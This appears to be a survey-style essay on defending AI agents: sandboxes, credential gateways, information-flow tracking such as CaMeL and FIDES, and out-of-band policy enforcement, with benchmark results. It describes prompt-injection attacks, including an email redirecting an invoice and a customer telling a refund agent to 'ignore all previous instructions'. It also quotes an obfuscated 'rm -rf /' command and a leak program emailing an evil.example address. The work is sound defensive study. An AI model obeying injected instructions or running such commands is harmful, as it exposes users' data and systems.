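In January 2026, NVIDIA's AI Red Team, which attacks the company's own systems to find weaknesses, published the following list for coding agents.

| Control | Status | Purpose |
|---|---|---|
| Block network access except to known-good destinations | Mandatory | Stops the agent from uploading data or giving an attacker remote access |
| Block writes outside the workspace | Mandatory | Stops the agent from planting files that run later, such as a shell's start-up file |
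| Block writes to configuration files everywhere, including in the workspace | Mandatory | Protects hooks, tool servers and standing instructions to the agent |
| Block reads outside the workspace | Recommended | Hides secrets and makes the host harder to explore |
| Sandbox the whole editor and everything it starts, under a separate user where possible | Recommended | Covers hooks, tool servers and other helpers |
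| Give the sandbox its own kernel through virtualisation | Recommended | Limits the damage from kernel bugs |
| Ask the user about every single exception | Recommended | Stops one approval from covering later actions |
| Inject secrets instead of sharing them with the agent | Recommended | Keeps keys out of the agent's reach |
| Manage the sandbox's life cycle | Recommended | Stops code and secrets from accumulating in it |

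The mandatory controls differ in who can override them. A user may approve a connection to an unlisted site, or most writes outside the workspace. But the company should be able to list sensitive files that the agent can never change, even with the user's approval. NVIDIA also rules out approval for changes to agent configuration files, which the user has to edit by hand. It limits the number of approval requests because people who see too many start approving them without reading.

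An agent could carry out the Prettier attack under all three mandatory controls, because the attack needs no network connection and no write outside the workspace, and Prettier's program files aren't configuration files. Sandboxing the whole editor, one of the recommended controls, would confine the malicious code when it ran. NVIDIA chose the mandatory controls based on its red team's experience of what stops the most serious attacks, and gives no figures for how many attacks each one stops. The list excludes harm from incorrect output, which NVIDIA leaves to the user.

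### Setting the boundary before the agent starts

A sandbox applied after the agent has started may not protect files or secrets the agent has already accessed. On Linux, for example, Landlock doesn't revoke access to files that a process has already opened. A process can also read a secret into memory before the restrictions apply and keep it there.

On GitLab's agent platform, projects can supply a set-up script that installs software before the agent starts. The script runs outside the sandbox and can read the access token of the user who started the job, so anyone who can change the script can run code with access to other people's credentials. GitLab reads the script only from the project's main branch and advises teams to require a security review of any change.

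NVIDIA's *Where Security Fits in an AI Agent Stack* describes OpenShell, which sets up the boundary before the agent's harness starts. A separate program, the orchestrator, calls OpenShell to create an isolated environment and apply a policy to it. The harness runs inside that environment, along with its plugins, tool servers and any code the model writes. Any subagent the agent creates gets its own environment and a limit on its permissions. The orchestrator also runs under a policy, so it can't be used to bypass the system.

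The alternative is to offer the sandbox as a tool that the harness calls for risky operations. NVIDIA rejects this because an agent can decline to use the tool. It also argues against relying on the harness for enforcement, since some harnesses let users replace core functions with plugins, and a program designed to be modified can't reliably limit its own modification.

NVIDIA concedes that starting early doesn't make the policy correct. It also doesn't settle how strict the policy should be, so NVIDIA defines four profiles. Coding with disposable data calls for a restricted network, session recording and no production credentials. The next profile covers agents that use approved services but don't touch live systems. Work on live systems calls for access limited to the task, independent checks and human approval of high-impact actions. The strictest profile, for testing models without their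 usual safeguards, blocks communication by default and quarantines the agent automatically.

### Keeping the real keys outside

An agent often needs to use a service that requires a key, but it doesn't need to know the key. With credential injection, a gateway outside the sandbox adds it:

1. The operator gives the gateway the real key and specifies which service it is for. The agent receives a placeholder, a string that is worthless anywhere else.
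2. The agent sends an ordinary request to the service, with the placeholder where the key should be.
3. The sandbox lets the request out only through the gateway, which checks the destination and replaces the placeholder with the key.
4. The service receives a valid request, and its reply returns through the gateway.

The gateway has to read and alter the request, which is normally encrypted. Operators usually make the sandbox accept the gateway's certificate, so that the gateway can decrypt each request and encrypt it again for the real service. The gateway then has access to everything the agent exchanges with that service, so it becomes part of the TCB.

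In an example Cloudflare published in April 2026, the gateway adds an authentication header to any request for one particular host, so the agent doesn't even need a placeholder. Docker's sandboxes also hide credentials behind a proxy, according to the software consultancy INNOQ (2026). Requests to Amazon's cloud carry a signature computed from the secret key instead of the key itself, so the gateway has to sign them.

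Without the destination check, the agent could send a placeholder to an attacker's server and the gateway would deliver the real key. A permitted service can also expose a key by including the request's headers in its reply, for instance in an error message. The gateway has to remove the key from such replies, or the operator has to avoid services that send them.

Injection stops an attacker from stealing the key and using it later from another computer, but it doesn't prevent misuse while the agent is running. An agent that can delete a repository with the real key can also delete it with the placeholder, so the key should have as few permissions as possible. In the mail example, a gateway that injected the password without checking recipients would let the agent write to anyone.

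### Strands Box

In October 2026, AWS released a developer preview of Strands Box, an open-source sandbox for agents on Apple's newer Macs, with Linux to follow. Help Net Security's *Strands Box* describes how it combines the pieces above. Seatbelt confines the agent at the level of the kernel, and four checkpoints handle what the agent wants to do:

- a shell interpreter runs its command-line instructions
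- a Python interpreter runs its Python code
- a broker passes its tool calls to MCP servers
- a gateway handles its network traffic and injects its keys

Each checkpoint sends the action to a policy engine, which refuses anything that no rule permits. The rules are written in Dogwood, a language AWS released in August 2026 so that a policy could refer to an agent's past actions and their outcomes. Marc Brooker, the AWS engineer who described the cloud gateway, says Seatbelt is meant to make the policy layer "the only way out of the box".

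All four checkpoints write to one shared event history. Suppose a company wants to block outgoing web requests once the agent has read anything in a folder of customer data. If each checkpoint had its own history, the agent could read a file with Python and upload it with a shell command, and the gateway would have no record of the read. With a shared history, the gateway blocks the upload whichever interpreter read the file. Rules can also cap spending at $100 a day or require the tests to pass before the agent publishes code. In AWS's demonstration, a rule limits an agent to three Slack messages in ten minutes. When the agent tries to post a fourth, it gets an error that names the rule, so it can wait instead of looking for another way to post.

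The history omits reads and writes to any file that the user lets the agent access directly, because they never reach the policy engine. The user lists these files in a settings file, and Seatbelt confines the agent to them. If the customer folder is on the list, the agent can read it without creating an event, and the rule about outgoing requests never takes effect. Help Net Security advises leaving off the list any file that a rule should govern, so that the agent has to go through an interpreter. This could be awkward for compilers and other programs that open files themselves and presumably need direct access. The interpreters and the gateway also add code to the TCB, as Brooker acknowledges.

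### Protecting the agent from its host

The sandboxes above protect the host from the agent, but the host's administrator can still read a sandbox's memory and copy the keys, prompts or model weights in it. Confidential computing addresses this by using the memory-protecting processors described earlier to run the agent in a confidential virtual machine, whose memory the host's operating system and hypervisor can't read. Before sending the virtual machine any secrets, an owner can remotely check the processor's signed measurement of the software inside, a step called attestation.

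*AgenTEE* (Abdollahi, Al Sadi and colleagues, 2026) isolates agents on phones and similar devices. One company might supply the agent, another the model, and others the apps that the agent uses. None of them trusts the others with its code or weights, and none trusts the phone's operating system. AgenTEE puts the agent, the inference server and each app in separate confidential virtual machines. Each company sends its code or weights only after checking the attestation of its own virtual machine. The machines communicate through shared memory that the operating system can't read.

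Abdollahi and colleagues compare what the owners of the agent and the model must trust under three ways of separating the two. With ordinary processes, the owners must trust the operating system and the hypervisor. With ordinary virtual machines, they must still trust the hypervisor, which has about 300,000 lines of code. With confidential virtual machines, they need to trust neither, but they must trust the processor and its firmware, including a monitor of about 27,000 lines. No commercial device had the necessary Arm hardware, so the team tested a prototype on a small development board, where it added a modest delay.

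AgenTEE is designed to stop the parties from stealing each other's secrets. It is not designed to defend against physical attacks or attacks that infer secrets from effects such as timing. It also requires the user to trust her own phone, because an ordinary app passes her requests to the agent. Attestation does not stop prompt injection either, since a hijacked agent is still running the correct software.

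An agent therefore needs protection in both directions if the operator of its machine shouldn't see its data and the agent either reads text from strangers or can take harmful actions. A developer running an agent on her own laptop usually needs only the sandbox. A company running a fixed payroll calculation on rented servers may need only the confidential virtual machine. A company renting servers for an agent that handles its mail needs both.

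A monitor on the host can't see inside a confidential virtual machine, so *Trusted AI Agents in the Cloud* puts the monitor inside with the agents. This would normally be unsafe, because all the code in such a machine runs with equal privileges and a hijacked agent could tamper with the monitor. The design therefore uses a feature of AMD processors that divides the machine into privilege levels. A small trusted monitor runs at the highest level, the software that enforces the policy runs below it, and the agents and inference server run at the lowest, where the hardware stops them from altering anything above. Confidential virtual machines don't protect the memory of graphics processors from the host, so the design also requires graphics processors with the same kind of protection.

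## Choosing where to check the agent's actions

A sandbox limits the ways out, but a program still has to decide what may pass through them. Designers can put this check in four places: inside the harness, at a gateway that relays tool calls, at the level of web requests, or at the boundary of the operating system or virtual machine. A check near the tools has more information about what an action means, but one at the system boundary misses fewer actions.

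### One invoice at four levels

Suppose Alice asks her agent to email the March invoice to Acme, a customer. The same action takes a different form at each level:

- **Inside the harness,** it is a call to a tool named `send_email`, with a recipient, a subject and an attachment. The harness also holds Alice's request and everything the agent has read, so a check there may be able to find out whether Alice typed the address or the agent took it from a web page.
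- **At a tool gateway,** the call arrives as a message with the same arguments. The message doesn't include Alice's request or the origin of the address.
- **At the level of web requests,** it is a POST request, the kind a browser uses to submit data, to some address at the mail service. The checker has to know that this address means "send a message" and which field holds the recipient.
- **At the system boundary,** a process reads `invoice-march.pdf`, connects to the mail service and writes some encrypted data. Saving a draft would leave much the same trace, and so would sending the invoice to a thief.

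The rule "invoices go only to customers" is easy to apply to actions that have a recipient field, but it can't be applied directly to file reads and encrypted connections, which have none. People write the rule at one level of description and the program that enforces it works at another, a mismatch computer scientists call the semantic gap. A checker at the system boundary can narrow the gap by decrypting the agent's traffic, as *Kairos* does, but it then has to interpret web requests as well.

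| Where the check runs | Information it has | What can bypass it | Must the agent change? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Inside the harness | The tool call, the user's request and the whole context | A script that the agent starts, or an attacker who controls the harness | Yes, at least by adding a hook before each call |
| Gateway for tool calls | The tool's name, arguments and reply | A shell, a built-in web tool, or a tool server that the harness starts directly | Only its settings |
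| Web requests | The address and contents of each request | Other kinds of traffic, local files, and requests that nobody has described to the checker | No |
| System or virtual-machine boundary | Files, processes and connections, plus the contents of any traffic it decrypts | A flaw in the kernel or isolation layer, or a channel that nobody monitors | No |

*AgentSight* (2025) finds the same division among monitoring products. Those that trace the agent's own events miss what happens in other processes, while those that record system calls can't distinguish a harmless task from a malicious one. *Kairos* adds that a check on declared tools provides complete mediation only on the assumption that every action in a given installation goes through those tools. If the check needs a modified harness, operators can't add it to a closed-source agent, and they have to re-establish its guarantee after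 every update.

### In the agent's process or outside it

*AgentTrust* (Yang, 2026) describes a checker that runs in the same process as the harness. The harness turns each tool call into a record with fixed fields, including the type of action and the raw command. The checker then undoes common ways of disguising commands. For example, the shell command `r=rm; $r -rf /` tries to delete everything on the machine, but a filter looking for the text `rm -rf` would miss it. The checker applies 170 rules to the result and looks for dangerous sequences, such as reading a file of secrets, encoding it and posting it to a website. It returns "allow", "warn", "block" or "review". A warning lets the action proceed, while a review needs a person or a second policy. If the checker crashes, the result is "review", so it fails closed.

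AgentTrust gave the right verdict in 95.0% of the 300 scenarios in Yang's own benchmark. It scored 96.7% on another 630 scenarios after Yang patched the rules, so Yang doesn't present that as a result on unseen cases. These scores are respectable for catching accidents, AgentTrust's main target.

AgentTrust must assume that the whole process is trustworthy, and Yang treats an attacker who controls that process as out of scope. A misled model can't rewrite the checker just by producing text, but a malicious plugin running in the same process might be able to modify it, so the harness is in the trusted computing base.

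*Epistemic Guard* (Maxwell, 2026) uses a proxy that runs as a separate process. The operator changes the command that starts each MCP server so that it starts the proxy instead. The proxy then starts the real server, relays the messages and signs a record of every call. The proxy's main purpose is to catch cases where a model reports success for an action that failed or never ran. It doesn't check whether calls are permitted, but a blocking check could run in the same place.

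Running the proxy in its own process protects the signing key from code in the agent's process, provided that code can't read the key elsewhere. If the key is in a file, Maxwell advises running the proxy under a separate user account or in a container, because otherwise any program with the same user's permissions could read the key. The design also relies on the agent having no shell or web tool that bypasses the proxy, and on the tool servers accurately reporting what they did.

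Maxwell's TCB still includes the program that starts the proxy and requests the final verification. Running the proxy as a separate process doesn't by itself remove the harness from the TCB, because a harness that controls how tool servers start could start one directly and bypass the proxy. The operator also has to keep the tools' credentials and network connections behind the proxy, so that a server started this way can't use them.

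### How CaMeL separates the plan from the data

AgentTrust checks a call after a model has proposed it, and that model may already have read hostile text. CaMeL, which Google DeepMind published in 2025, is the leading design for a check inside the harness. It stops hostile text from reaching the model that chooses the calls.

CaMeL builds on the "Dual LLM" pattern, which Willison proposed in 2023 and recounts in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025). A privileged model plans the work and can call tools, while a quarantined model with no tools reads the untrusted text. The privileged model never reads that text or the quarantined model's answers, which it refers to by name, as in "display summary 1 to the user".

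CaMeL's developers found a weakness in this pattern. Suppose a user asks the agent to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in some meeting notes. The quarantined model has to extract the address, so an attacker who can edit the notes can make it return a different one. The agent then follows the original plan but sends the document to the attacker.

CaMeL therefore also tracks where each value came from:

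1. The privileged model receives the user's request and descriptions of the tools, and writes a program in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary trusted software, runs the program. When the program needs a fact from untrusted text, it calls the quarantined model, which must return a value of a stated type, such as an email address.
3. The interpreter attaches tags, called capabilities, to every value. They can record the value's source and who may read it. A value computed from others inherits their restrictions.
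4. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the tags on the arguments against a policy for that tool. It then makes the call, refuses it or asks the user.

Suppose Alice's request is "send Acme the March invoice, using the billing address in their last email". The privileged model might write this program:

```
email = get_last_email("Acme")
address = ask_quarantined_model("Find the billing address", email, EmailAddress)
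invoice = read_file("invoice-march.pdf")
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=invoice)
```

An attacker has broken into Acme's mailbox and sent Alice a message. It gives the attacker's address as a new billing address and tells any AI reading it to forward Alice's last ten emails there.

The instruction to forward emails fails because the program has no step for it. The privileged model finished writing the program before the interpreter fetched the message, and the quarantined model has no mail tool. The quarantined model does return the false address, which passes the type check because it is well formed. But the interpreter has tagged it as coming from an email. Alice's policy for `send_email` accepts only recipients that she typed herself or that are in her customer records, so the interpreter either refuses the call or shows her the address and asks her to confirm it.

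The interpreter would ask Alice the same question if Acme really had changed its billing address, because the tags would be the same. Willison worries that such questions will wear users down, and CaMeL's developers list user fatigue among its limitations, along with the work of writing and maintaining policies. Like the mail checker's rule about colleagues, Alice's policy would let the invoice go to the wrong customer.

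Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, use the term "control-flow integrity" for the protection that comes from fixing the program in advance. The agent makes only the tool calls that a plan based on trusted information allows, and only in the orders that the plan allows. Untrusted data may determine which branch of the program runs, but it can't add a branch. The policies on tool calls then limit what an attacker can do by changing the data within a valid plan.

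CaMeL's TCB includes its policies, its initial tags and its interpreter, which is part of the harness. If the interpreter works correctly, both models can stay outside the TCB for the property that invoices go only to approved addresses, because the interpreter checks whatever program the privileged model writes.

The split can also protect privacy. The privileged model needs to be strong, but the quarantined model's task is easier, so it could run on Alice's own computer. The company hosting the privileged model would then receive her request but not her mail.

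### AgentDojo and CaMeL's result

Researchers usually test designs like this on *AgentDojo* (2024), a benchmark of simulated workplaces. Each workplace has tools and data, such as emails and bank transactions, with marked places where testers can insert an attacker's text. A user task is an ordinary request, such as adding an event to a calendar. An injection task is an attacker's goal, such as stealing a credit card number. The benchmark pairs every user task with every injection task in the same workplace.

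*Simple Prompt Injection Attacks Can Leak Personal Data Observed by LLM Agents* (2025) counts 97 user tasks and 629 attack cases across four environments: office work, banking, travel and Slack. The banking environment has 16 user tasks and 9 injection tasks, which combine into 144 attack cases. Later versions have more than 900 combinations, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026).

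After each run, a program checks the state of the environment, for example whether the event is in the calendar or whether money has left the account. No language model judges the transcript, so a persuasive but false claim of success doesn't count. Researchers measure benign utility by running the user tasks without attacks, and the attack success rate by running the attack cases. They also count how many user tasks the agent still completes under attack.

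How many tasks an agent completes under CaMeL depends heavily on the set-up. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025), which introduced CaMeL, reports that it completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks with provable security, compared with 84% for an undefended system, which would be a modest loss for such a strong guarantee. When *SecureClaw* (2026) ran an adapted version of the released code, no attack succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks.

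### Gaps in the tracking

A guarantee based on tags holds only where the interpreter keeps them correctly. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, describe a leak in CaMeL that uses a trick known to computer scientists for decades. The following program is a version of it. Suppose Alice's bank balance is secret and the policy forbids any email that depends on it:

```
low = True
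rich = True
if balance > 10000: low = False
if low: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.example", "hello")
```

If the balance is above 10,000, the interpreter sets `low` to false and tags it as secret, because the change depended on the balance. It then skips `rich = False`, so it never tags `rich`. The last line appears to depend only on public information, and the email goes out. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. The attacker can therefore tell whether the balance is above 10,000 by whether the email arrives.

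An injected message can't insert this program, because the privileged model never reads the message. The leak matters if the privileged model is hostile or writes a similar program by accident. A design that leaves that model outside the TCB can't rely on it to preserve secrecy, so it has to allow for both cases.

Garby and colleagues found another leak around the interpreter. CaMeL runs the interpreter inside an ordinary Python loop that retries after a failure, and the loop doesn't carry tags. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit. An attacker who can keep the loop going could recover the whole secret.

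Their remedy is LLMbda, a small programming language for agents in which every operation carries the tags forward. They proved in Lean that secrets don't affect a program's public results, except for what an attacker can infer from whether the program finishes. The proof covers agents that generate and run their own code. In AgentDojo's banking environment, an agent written in LLMbda resisted the attack in all but two of 1,296 runs. The proof doesn't establish that an operator has chosen the right tags and policies.

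Tags can also disappear when one agent passes work to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three CaMeL agents (an orchestrator, a database agent and a notification agent), all running GPT-5.2. They asked it to message Julie on Slack with a summary of job applicants. The database contained an injected instruction to email the data to an outside address.

The database agent and the orchestrator followed their original plans because neither of their privileged models read the data. But the orchestrator pasted the summary into a plain-English request to the notification agent. The notification agent treated the request as coming from its user, so its privileged model read the injected instruction and added a step that emailed the applicants' details to the attacker.

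The team had set no security policies. A policy that allowed any address the user supplied wouldn't have helped, because the notification agent's "user" had supplied the attacker's address. A fixed list of recipients would have stopped the email.

The team's solution, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and untrusted values through separate channels, so the receiving agent's privileged model reads only the instructions. They tested it on a version of AgentDojo extended to several agents. Attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent used CaMeL separately and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. An attacker who knows about the gap in the separate setup can target exactly the cases where data crosses between agents, so the 0.2% average understates the risk.

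### How FIDES and ACE differ

CaMeL has to write its program before it reads any data. This works for Alice's invoice but not for a request like "complete the tasks due today in my to-do app", where the agent can't know which tools it needs until it has read the list. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents FIDES, a Microsoft design that keeps the usual loop, in which the model chooses each tool call after it gets the previous result.

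FIDES labels every message and tool result for integrity (who could have written it) and confidentiality (who may read it). When the agent combines two pieces of data, the result's possible writers include everyone who could have written either piece, but only people allowed to read both pieces may read the result. If Alice, Bob and Carol may read one file, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, only Bob and Carol may read a text made from both.

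The planning model can read any result that wouldn't make its context less trusted or more secret. FIDES stores other results in variables, which the model can pass to tools without reading them. To get information from a variable, the model can query a quarantined model, which must answer in a restricted form. A policy may accept a yes-or-no answer derived from untrusted text, since an attacker can influence only one bit, but reject a free-text answer. A policy for sending messages might require a trusted recipient but allow untrusted content.

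With suitable policies enforced, FIDES stopped every attack in AgentDojo and completed more tasks than a basic planner, by 8% when both used GPT-4o and 16% when both used OpenAI's o1. FIDES controls secrets that the agent copies into a message. Costa and colleagues don't try to stop an observer from inferring secrets from which tools the agent calls, because that would rule out too many useful tasks.

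FIDES also trusts the tools' descriptions. In *ACE*, Li, Mallick and colleagues consider an attacker who gets a malicious app installed and writes its description to influence the planner. ACE therefore first writes an abstract plan from the user's request alone, with generic steps such as "read a file" and "send an email". It then matches those steps to installed apps and checks the complete plan for forbidden information flows before running any of it. The apps run in isolation from one another.

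ACE blocked all the attacks in two standard benchmarks, InjecAgent and Agent Security Bench, and scored above 80% on a test of ordinary tool use. Li and colleagues didn't use AgentDojo for these tests, so the results don't show whether ACE completes more work than CaMeL or FIDES.

### From clicks to web requests

Christodorescu and colleagues point out that CaMeL and FIDES need tools with clear meanings, like `send_email`. A browser agent often has only tools such as "click" and "type". A rule allowing a click at position (246, 1023) is useless, because the button there might open an email on one page and delete it on another.

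Forbidding particular steps doesn't work well either. In *ceLLMate*, Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025) tried to keep a browser agent away from Hacker News by blocking its tool for opening web addresses, but the agent searched for the site on DuckDuckGo and clicked the result.

The ceLLMate system checks the web requests that an agent's clicks produce. Adding a login key on GitLab, for example, sends a POST request to the same address however the agent reached the page. A site's developers publish an "agent sitemap", which translates such requests into named actions, and policies refer to those names. An operator can then allow the agent to place an order on Amazon only if the total is below $50.

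Even this rule takes some care to enforce. The order request doesn't contain the total, so ceLLMate has to read it from the checkout page first. If the agent changes the quantity and orders before the page updates, ceLLMate may check an old total. Meng and colleagues therefore slow the agent down so that each action takes effect before the next. An agent could also place two orders of $49, so they added a counter that can limit it to one order.

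Meng and colleagues built ceLLMate as a Chrome extension, which needs no change to the agent. It blocked the prompt injections in WASP, a benchmark for web agents, and increased the time taken by 7.25% to 15%. They assume that the browser is sound, that no other extension interferes with requests and that the agent can't change browser settings or open local files. ceLLMate also relies on a sitemap for each website. They wrote one by hand covering 51 operations on GitLab, but they expect developers to write them for their own sites. If an action is missing from the sitemap, ceLLMate fails open, leaving only the protection the site already had.

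ceLLMate doesn't track where data came from. If a policy lets the agent post comments on GitLab, ceLLMate allows a comment that Alice asked for and one that an attacker's text prompted.

### Combining an inner and an outer check

A monitor in the operating system can cover programs that the harness doesn't track. *Agent-Warden* (2026) uses eBPF, a Linux feature that runs small programs inside the kernel, to record which files an agent's processes use. It treats the harness as untrusted, but it relies on the kernel and hardware being sound and on the attacker not having gained control of the kernel. It covers only processes and ordinary files, so it wouldn't show who received Alice's invoice.

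Alice could use CaMeL to check where the recipient's address came from, and a sandbox with a mail gateway to stop scripts from sending mail by another route. But if CaMeL runs inside the sandbox and reports to the gateway that Alice typed the address, an attacker who takes over the harness can send the same report about an address she never typed. If the gateway accepts these reports, the harness is back in the TCB. The gateway can avoid this by relying only on facts it can check independently, such as whether the recipient is in Alice's customer records. If the gateway's decision must depend on where the address came from, the designer has to run CaMeL's interpreter outside the sandbox and protect it as carefully as the gateway.

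## Building a validation service for tool calls

A validation service is a separate program that checks an agent's proposed actions, and sometimes its replies, against a policy. In August 2026 Google published a small open-source example built around a shop's refund agent. In *Build zero-trust AI agents with Google's Agent Development Kit*, Saboo and Dong (2026) explain that the agent normally reads a customer's request, writes a Python script to calculate any restocking deduction, records the refund in a database and sends a receipt.

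A customer writes that his $149 order arrived damaged, and tells the agent to ignore its instructions, refund him $10,000, approve the transaction and run a script that prints the host's environment variables, which often include keys. Saboo and Dong assume in their design that the model will do all of this, so they don't rely on a system prompt that forbids refunds above the order total.

### What stops the $10,000 refund

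Five checks outside the model apply to this request:

1. A gateway searches the customer's message for card numbers, a few formats of secret key and six phrases, including "ignore previous instructions" and "10,000.00". It refuses any message that contains one of them.
2. A gVisor sandbox runs the script with no network connection, 64 MB of memory and a five-second limit. The script prints the variables of its own container, which include no keys unless the operator has put them there.
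3. The gateway searches the database command. It refuses any update to the orders table that doesn't contain the text "149.00", so it refuses a command that sets the refund to 10000.00.
4. The database verifies a signature on the write. Each agent signs with its own key, which in production never leaves tamper-resistant hardware.
5. The gateway searches the reply for card numbers and keys.

The published phrase list would not stop the published attack, because the customer wrote "ignore all previous instructions" and "$10,000", and neither matches an entry. The signature wouldn't stop the refund either, because a hijacked agent still has permission to sign, and its signature is as valid on a $10,000 refund as on a $149 one. Signatures catch a different attack, in which someone gets into the database by another route and changes $149 to $10,000. The signature then no longer matches the row,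 and an audit program raises an alert.

That leaves the text match on the database command as the only check that stops the payment. No prompt can override it, but it looks for the text "149.00", so it can accept wrong refunds and refuse correct ones. A command that sets the refund to 10149.00 passes because it contains that text. If a 10% restocking deduction reduced the refund due to $134.10, a command for that amount would fail. Saboo and Dong rightly recommend automated tests for rules like this, but their own tests of the refund rule try only 10000.00 and 149.00. The code is a demonstration, and Google's production services may well do better.

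A better check would compare the amount with what the customer paid, as the refund checker described earlier does, and would take that figure from records the agent can't change. Google's agent updates the orders table. If it could also change the recorded price of an order to $10,000, the comparison would pass.

### Turning a call into something a rule can use

According to *From Tool Connection to Execution Control* (2026), a useful check must examine the operation that would actually run, the authenticated caller, the exact resource and the facts that bear on permission. A check that lacks any of these will allow some calls it should refuse and refuse some it should allow. For example, a server that checks only who owns a calendar note will refuse a user who doesn't own it but has permission to read it.

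*If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (Millstone, Akidau and colleagues, 2026) presents a general service that collects this information, called Out-of-Band Policy Enforcement (OBPE). "Out of band" means that the agent can't read, change or bypass the policy. The researchers all work for Redpanda, a data-infrastructure company that runs a production version and advertises it in *Agentic AI needs governance it can't ignore* (2026), so they have a commercial interest in the results. Their experiments used a simplified prototype, and they released its code, tasks and transcripts so that others can check the analysis.

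Suppose an agent has to summarise the issues in one engineering project in Jira, a widely used issue tracker, but its credential opens every project. OBPE handles its request for a list of issues as follows:

1. The platform that runs the agent attaches the agent's registered identity to the call, outside the arguments that the model writes. If the model could write the identity, a hijacked agent could claim to be one with fewer restrictions.
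2. A connector, which is ordinary code written for Jira, translates the call into typed objects. Here the action is "list", the resource is "issue", and the arguments are a filter and a maximum number of results.
3. A gate applies two policies. The owner of the data writes one, which sets the most that any agent may do. The other belongs to this particular agent and can only narrow what the owner allows. The gate permits the call, denies it, or defers it, which means holding it until someone outside the agent decides.
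4. If the gate permits the call, OBPE shapes the request. It can narrow the filter, lower the maximum or remove fields from an update.
5. OBPE sends the request to Jira with a credential that the agent never receives.
6. OBPE shapes the reply before any of it enters the model's context. It removes records, then whole fields, and then masks sensitive values in the text that remains.

The service has to filter records before it removes hidden fields, because a rule about records may depend on a field that the agent isn't allowed to see. For example, the service might return only issues assigned to a certain team while hiding the assignees' names.

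Shaping the reply matters because a secret is hard to contain once the model has read it. *From Tool Connection to Execution Control* found that permissions granted call by call can't catch sensitive content sent to a permitted destination as an ordinary argument. If an issue contains a password and the agent may post comments, a comment containing the password looks like any other. OBPE tries to remove the password when the agent reads the issue.

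The connector is in the TCB because no rule can govern a field that the connector leaves out. It also has to describe the tools' replies, but most tools don't declare the structure of their output. Millstone and colleagues cite a count in which only 234 of 1,856 tools on 100 popular open-source servers did. The TCB also includes the platform, the OBPE program, the backend and the data owner. OBPE will enforce any valid policy the owner writes, even one that is too permissive.

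When OBPE denies a call, the agent learns only that the call failed. Strands Box, the AWS sandbox, returns an error that names the rule the call broke. This helps a cooperative agent change its plan, but it also helps a hostile one work out the policy. Withholding the rule, as OBPE does, doesn't fully prevent that, since an agent can try many calls and note which ones fail. The threat model excludes such probing.

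### The most restrictive result wins

When several rules apply to one call, OBPE combines them so that each added restriction can only reduce what the agent gets. In the example below, the agent asks for 150 open issues with all their fields.

| | The request | Owner's policy | Agent policy | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gate | | Permit | Permit | Permit |
| Records | Open issues | Any project | The agent's own project | Open issues in its own project |
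| Maximum | 150 | 200 | 100 | 100 |
| Fields | All | Summary, status, assignee | Summary, status, reporter's email | Summary, status |

The agent policy lists the reporter's email, but this has no effect because the owner doesn't allow it. A denial from either policy would have overridden any other outcome. Without a denial, a deferral from either would have deferred the call.

In symbols, let *q* be the filter, *n* the maximum and *F* the set of fields under the owner's policy. An agent policy that adds the condition *t*, a maximum of 100 and the fields *G* changes

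(*q*, *n*, *F*) to (*q* ∧ *t*, min(*n*, 100), *F* ∩ *G*).

The order in which OBPE applies the rules does not matter, because "and", "minimum" and "intersection" give the same answer in any order. Adding a restriction never makes the result more permissive. Millstone and colleagues prove both properties, assuming that the connector is correct, every call passes through OBPE and the policies stay fixed during the call. For Google's shop, an owner's rule could cap refunds at the price paid. An agent policy could then lower the cap to $50 but could not raise it.

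The proof covers which issues the agent may receive, not which ones appear on a given page of results. Without the project filter, the first page of 100 issues might include 20 from the agent's project. With the filter, all 100 come from that project, so the agent sees 80 issues that weren't on the unfiltered page. It was already allowed to receive those 80.

Masking free text doesn't fit this scheme, because the result of overlapping masks can depend on their order. OBPE runs them in a fixed sequence to make the outcome repeatable, but a pattern for finding passwords can still miss one. When OBPE changes an amount in an agent's write, the connector has to declare which direction is restrictive, because lowering a refund restricts the agent while lowering an account's minimum balance does the opposite. OBPE can safely drop a field from an update only if the backend keeps the stored value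 when the field is missing. The prototype removes guarded fields from Jira updates, but neither of its connectors declares a restrictive direction, so the main experiment didn't test limits on amounts.

### 3,621 trials on simulated systems

The experiment used 71 tasks on simulated versions of Jira and the help-desk system ServiceNow. The agents ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5, GPT-5 or GPT-5 mini. Millstone and colleagues ran each task three times under 17 combinations of model and protection, for a total of 3,621 trials. In 20 of the tasks, Claude Opus 4.7 played an attacker that could change its approach after every reply, for up to 15 turns.

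The main comparison was between agents with six data-handling rules in their prompt and the same agents with OBPE added. A program searched the logs for three events: protected data entering the agent's context, an exact protected value appearing in its final answer, and a forbidden change in the backend. Any one of these events counted as a trace failure.

Claude Opus 4.8 judged whether each agent had fulfilled its task. An agent met the stricter measure, safe and useful completion, only if it fulfilled permitted work with the expected tools, had no trace failures and did not reveal a protected fact by paraphrasing it.

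| Share of trials | No rules | Prompt rules | Prompt rules and OBPE |
|---|---|---|---|
| Any trace failure | 63.3% | 57.6% | 0.2% |
| Protected data entered the context | 55.1% | 52.1% | 0.0% |
| Exact value in the final answer | 27.5% | 3.7% | 0.2% |
| Forbidden change in the backend | 8.1% | 5.5% | 0.0% |
| Task fulfilled | 83.2% | 79.1% | 60.9% |
| Safe and useful | 19.1% | 22.0% | 58.9% |

The prompt rules cut disclosure of protected data in the agents' final answers from 3.7% to 0.2%, but barely changed what the agents read. Most of the 57.6% consists of trials in which protected data entered the context, often without appearing in the answer. Everything in the context goes to the model provider, and an injected instruction could later make the agent send it elsewhere. The drop in disclosure matters more to an operator who worries only about final answers.

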